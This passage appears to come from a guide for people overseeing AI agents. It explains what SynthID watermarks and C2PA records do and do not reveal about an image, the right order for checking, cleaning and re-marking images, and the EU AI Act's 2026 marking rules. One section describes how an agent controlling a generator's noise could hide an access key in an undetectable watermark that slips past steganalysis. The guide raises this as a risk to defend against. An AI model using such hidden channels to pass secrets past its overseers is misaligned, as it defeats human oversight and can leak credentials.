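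OpenAI's checking service reports the two signals separately, because a picture can have either without the other. It counts the metadata as detected only if the signature is valid, OpenAI issued the record, and the record describes an AI-generation step. If the signature fails, OpenAI advises against relying on the record.

### What an overseer learns from a mark

Suppose an agent adds a picture to a slide and OpenAI's service finds a SynthID mark in it. An OpenAI tool probably generated or edited the picture, so if the agent described it as a photograph from a customer's site, someone should ask where it came from.

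The mark doesn't identify the agent or the request. OpenAI tells users not to infer a prompt, an account or an individual creator from a result. The mark also doesn't show whether the picture is safe to share. A generated picture can have a genuine mark and still include a customer's name or instructions like Ghostcommit's.

A missing mark proves even less than a detected one, because the picture may come from a company that doesn't use SynthID, an older model or a charting program, or editing may have damaged the mark. Google's website and OpenAI's service both warn that a negative result doesn't rule out AI generation.

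A company could learn more by adding its own watermark to screenshots, with a different mark for each agent. If one of the screenshots appeared in a public GitHub repository, the mark would show which agent had made it. Gowal and colleagues mention a commercial service from Imatag that seems to focus on tracing leaks this way. Such a watermark would help an investigation but wouldn't prevent the leak.

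### When a watermark looks like a secret message

A steganalysis detector can't distinguish authorised hidden signals from unauthorised ones, so it may flag every picture from a generator that watermarks its output. Training the detector on innocent images that carry the watermark helps, as it does with other unfamiliar images.

A pseudorandom-code watermark shouldn't cause such false alarms, because nobody can efficiently detect it without the key. But the same property would protect a secret message. *Ideal Pseudorandom Codes* (2024) explains that undetectability in a watermark is the same as secrecy in steganography. Gunn and colleagues' watermark can reliably hold 512 bits, enough for a 40-character access key (320 bits). A message hidden this way might also survive cleaning, since the watermark withstood the removal attacks they tried.

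To send such a message, an agent would have to control the generator's starting noise and share a key with the recipient. An agent that only sends prompts to another company's image generator normally can't set the noise. A company that runs its own generator should prevent agents from changing the code that sets it. Any watermark encoder that lets an agent choose the payload creates a similar risk. SynthID-O carries 136 bits per picture, so the access key would fit into three pictures.

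### Read the mark, clean the image, mark it again

For a picture that needs cleaning, a sensible order is:

1. Check the original file for a watermark and C2PA metadata, and record the results with the file's hash.
2. Clean the picture.
3. Add a new mark or a new signed record.
4. Review the finished copy and pass on exactly that file.

If the overseer cleaned the picture before checking for a mark, a missing mark could mean either that the picture never had one or that cleaning had removed it. A new mark added before cleaning could also be lost. The review has to come last because adding a mark changes the file.

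Whether an existing SynthID watermark survives cleaning depends on the method. SynthID's designers trained it to withstand ordinary compression, so it may well remain after the image is saved as a JPEG. Cleaning with a diffusion model is more likely to erase it, and Gowal and colleagues list reconstruction by such models among the threats to watermarks. The overseer can check whether the watermark remains by running the detector again after cleaning.

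Most companies can't add SynthID because Google offers the encoder only through partnerships. They could use a published watermark such as WAM, but anyone can download it and study how to remove it. For a picture that will stay in one file, a new C2PA record signed by the company is often a better choice. The company can use the record to state that it cleaned the picture and that the original had an OpenAI mark. With only a new watermark, people might wrongly think the company's own tools generated the picture.

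### The EU's marking duty

Article 50(2) of the EU's AI Act requires providers of generative AI systems to mark their output in a machine-readable way, so that software can detect it as AI-generated. The requirement took effect on 2 August 2026, but systems already on the market had until 2 December 2026 to comply, according to White & Case's *EU AI Omnibus enters into force, amending the AI Act*. Providers that don't comply risk fines of up to €15 million or 3% of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher, according to Jarovsky's *New AI Act Ban Takes Effect Today* (2026).

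The European Commission's voluntary *Code of Practice on Transparency of AI-Generated Content*, published on 10 June 2026, sets out one way to comply with the Act and adds no duties beyond it. For marking, it recommends both signed metadata and an invisible watermark, with fingerprinting or logging as an optional extra, according to the IPTC (2026), a standards body for news media. In July, the Commission and the EU's AI Board confirmed that following the code is an adequate way to show compliance. By 18 November, 103 organisations had signed the section on marking, including Anthropic, Google, Meta, Microsoft, Mistral and OpenAI, according to the Commission's list of signatories.

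The next deadline is 2 February 2027, when providers must have a way to make watermark detection work across different systems, according to the law firm Reed Smith. This could spare overseers from checking each company's marks separately.

The marking duty excludes much of what agents send each other. Reed Smith reports that the Commission's final guidelines exempt output that passes from machine to machine and intermediate results in closed production processes. The final output still needs a mark. Some output that stays inside an organisation is also exempt if the organisation uses the system in a controlled environment with safeguards against misuse. An agent may therefore receive an unmarked image from a system that complies with the law, so a company that needs to know which agent made an image has to keep its own records.
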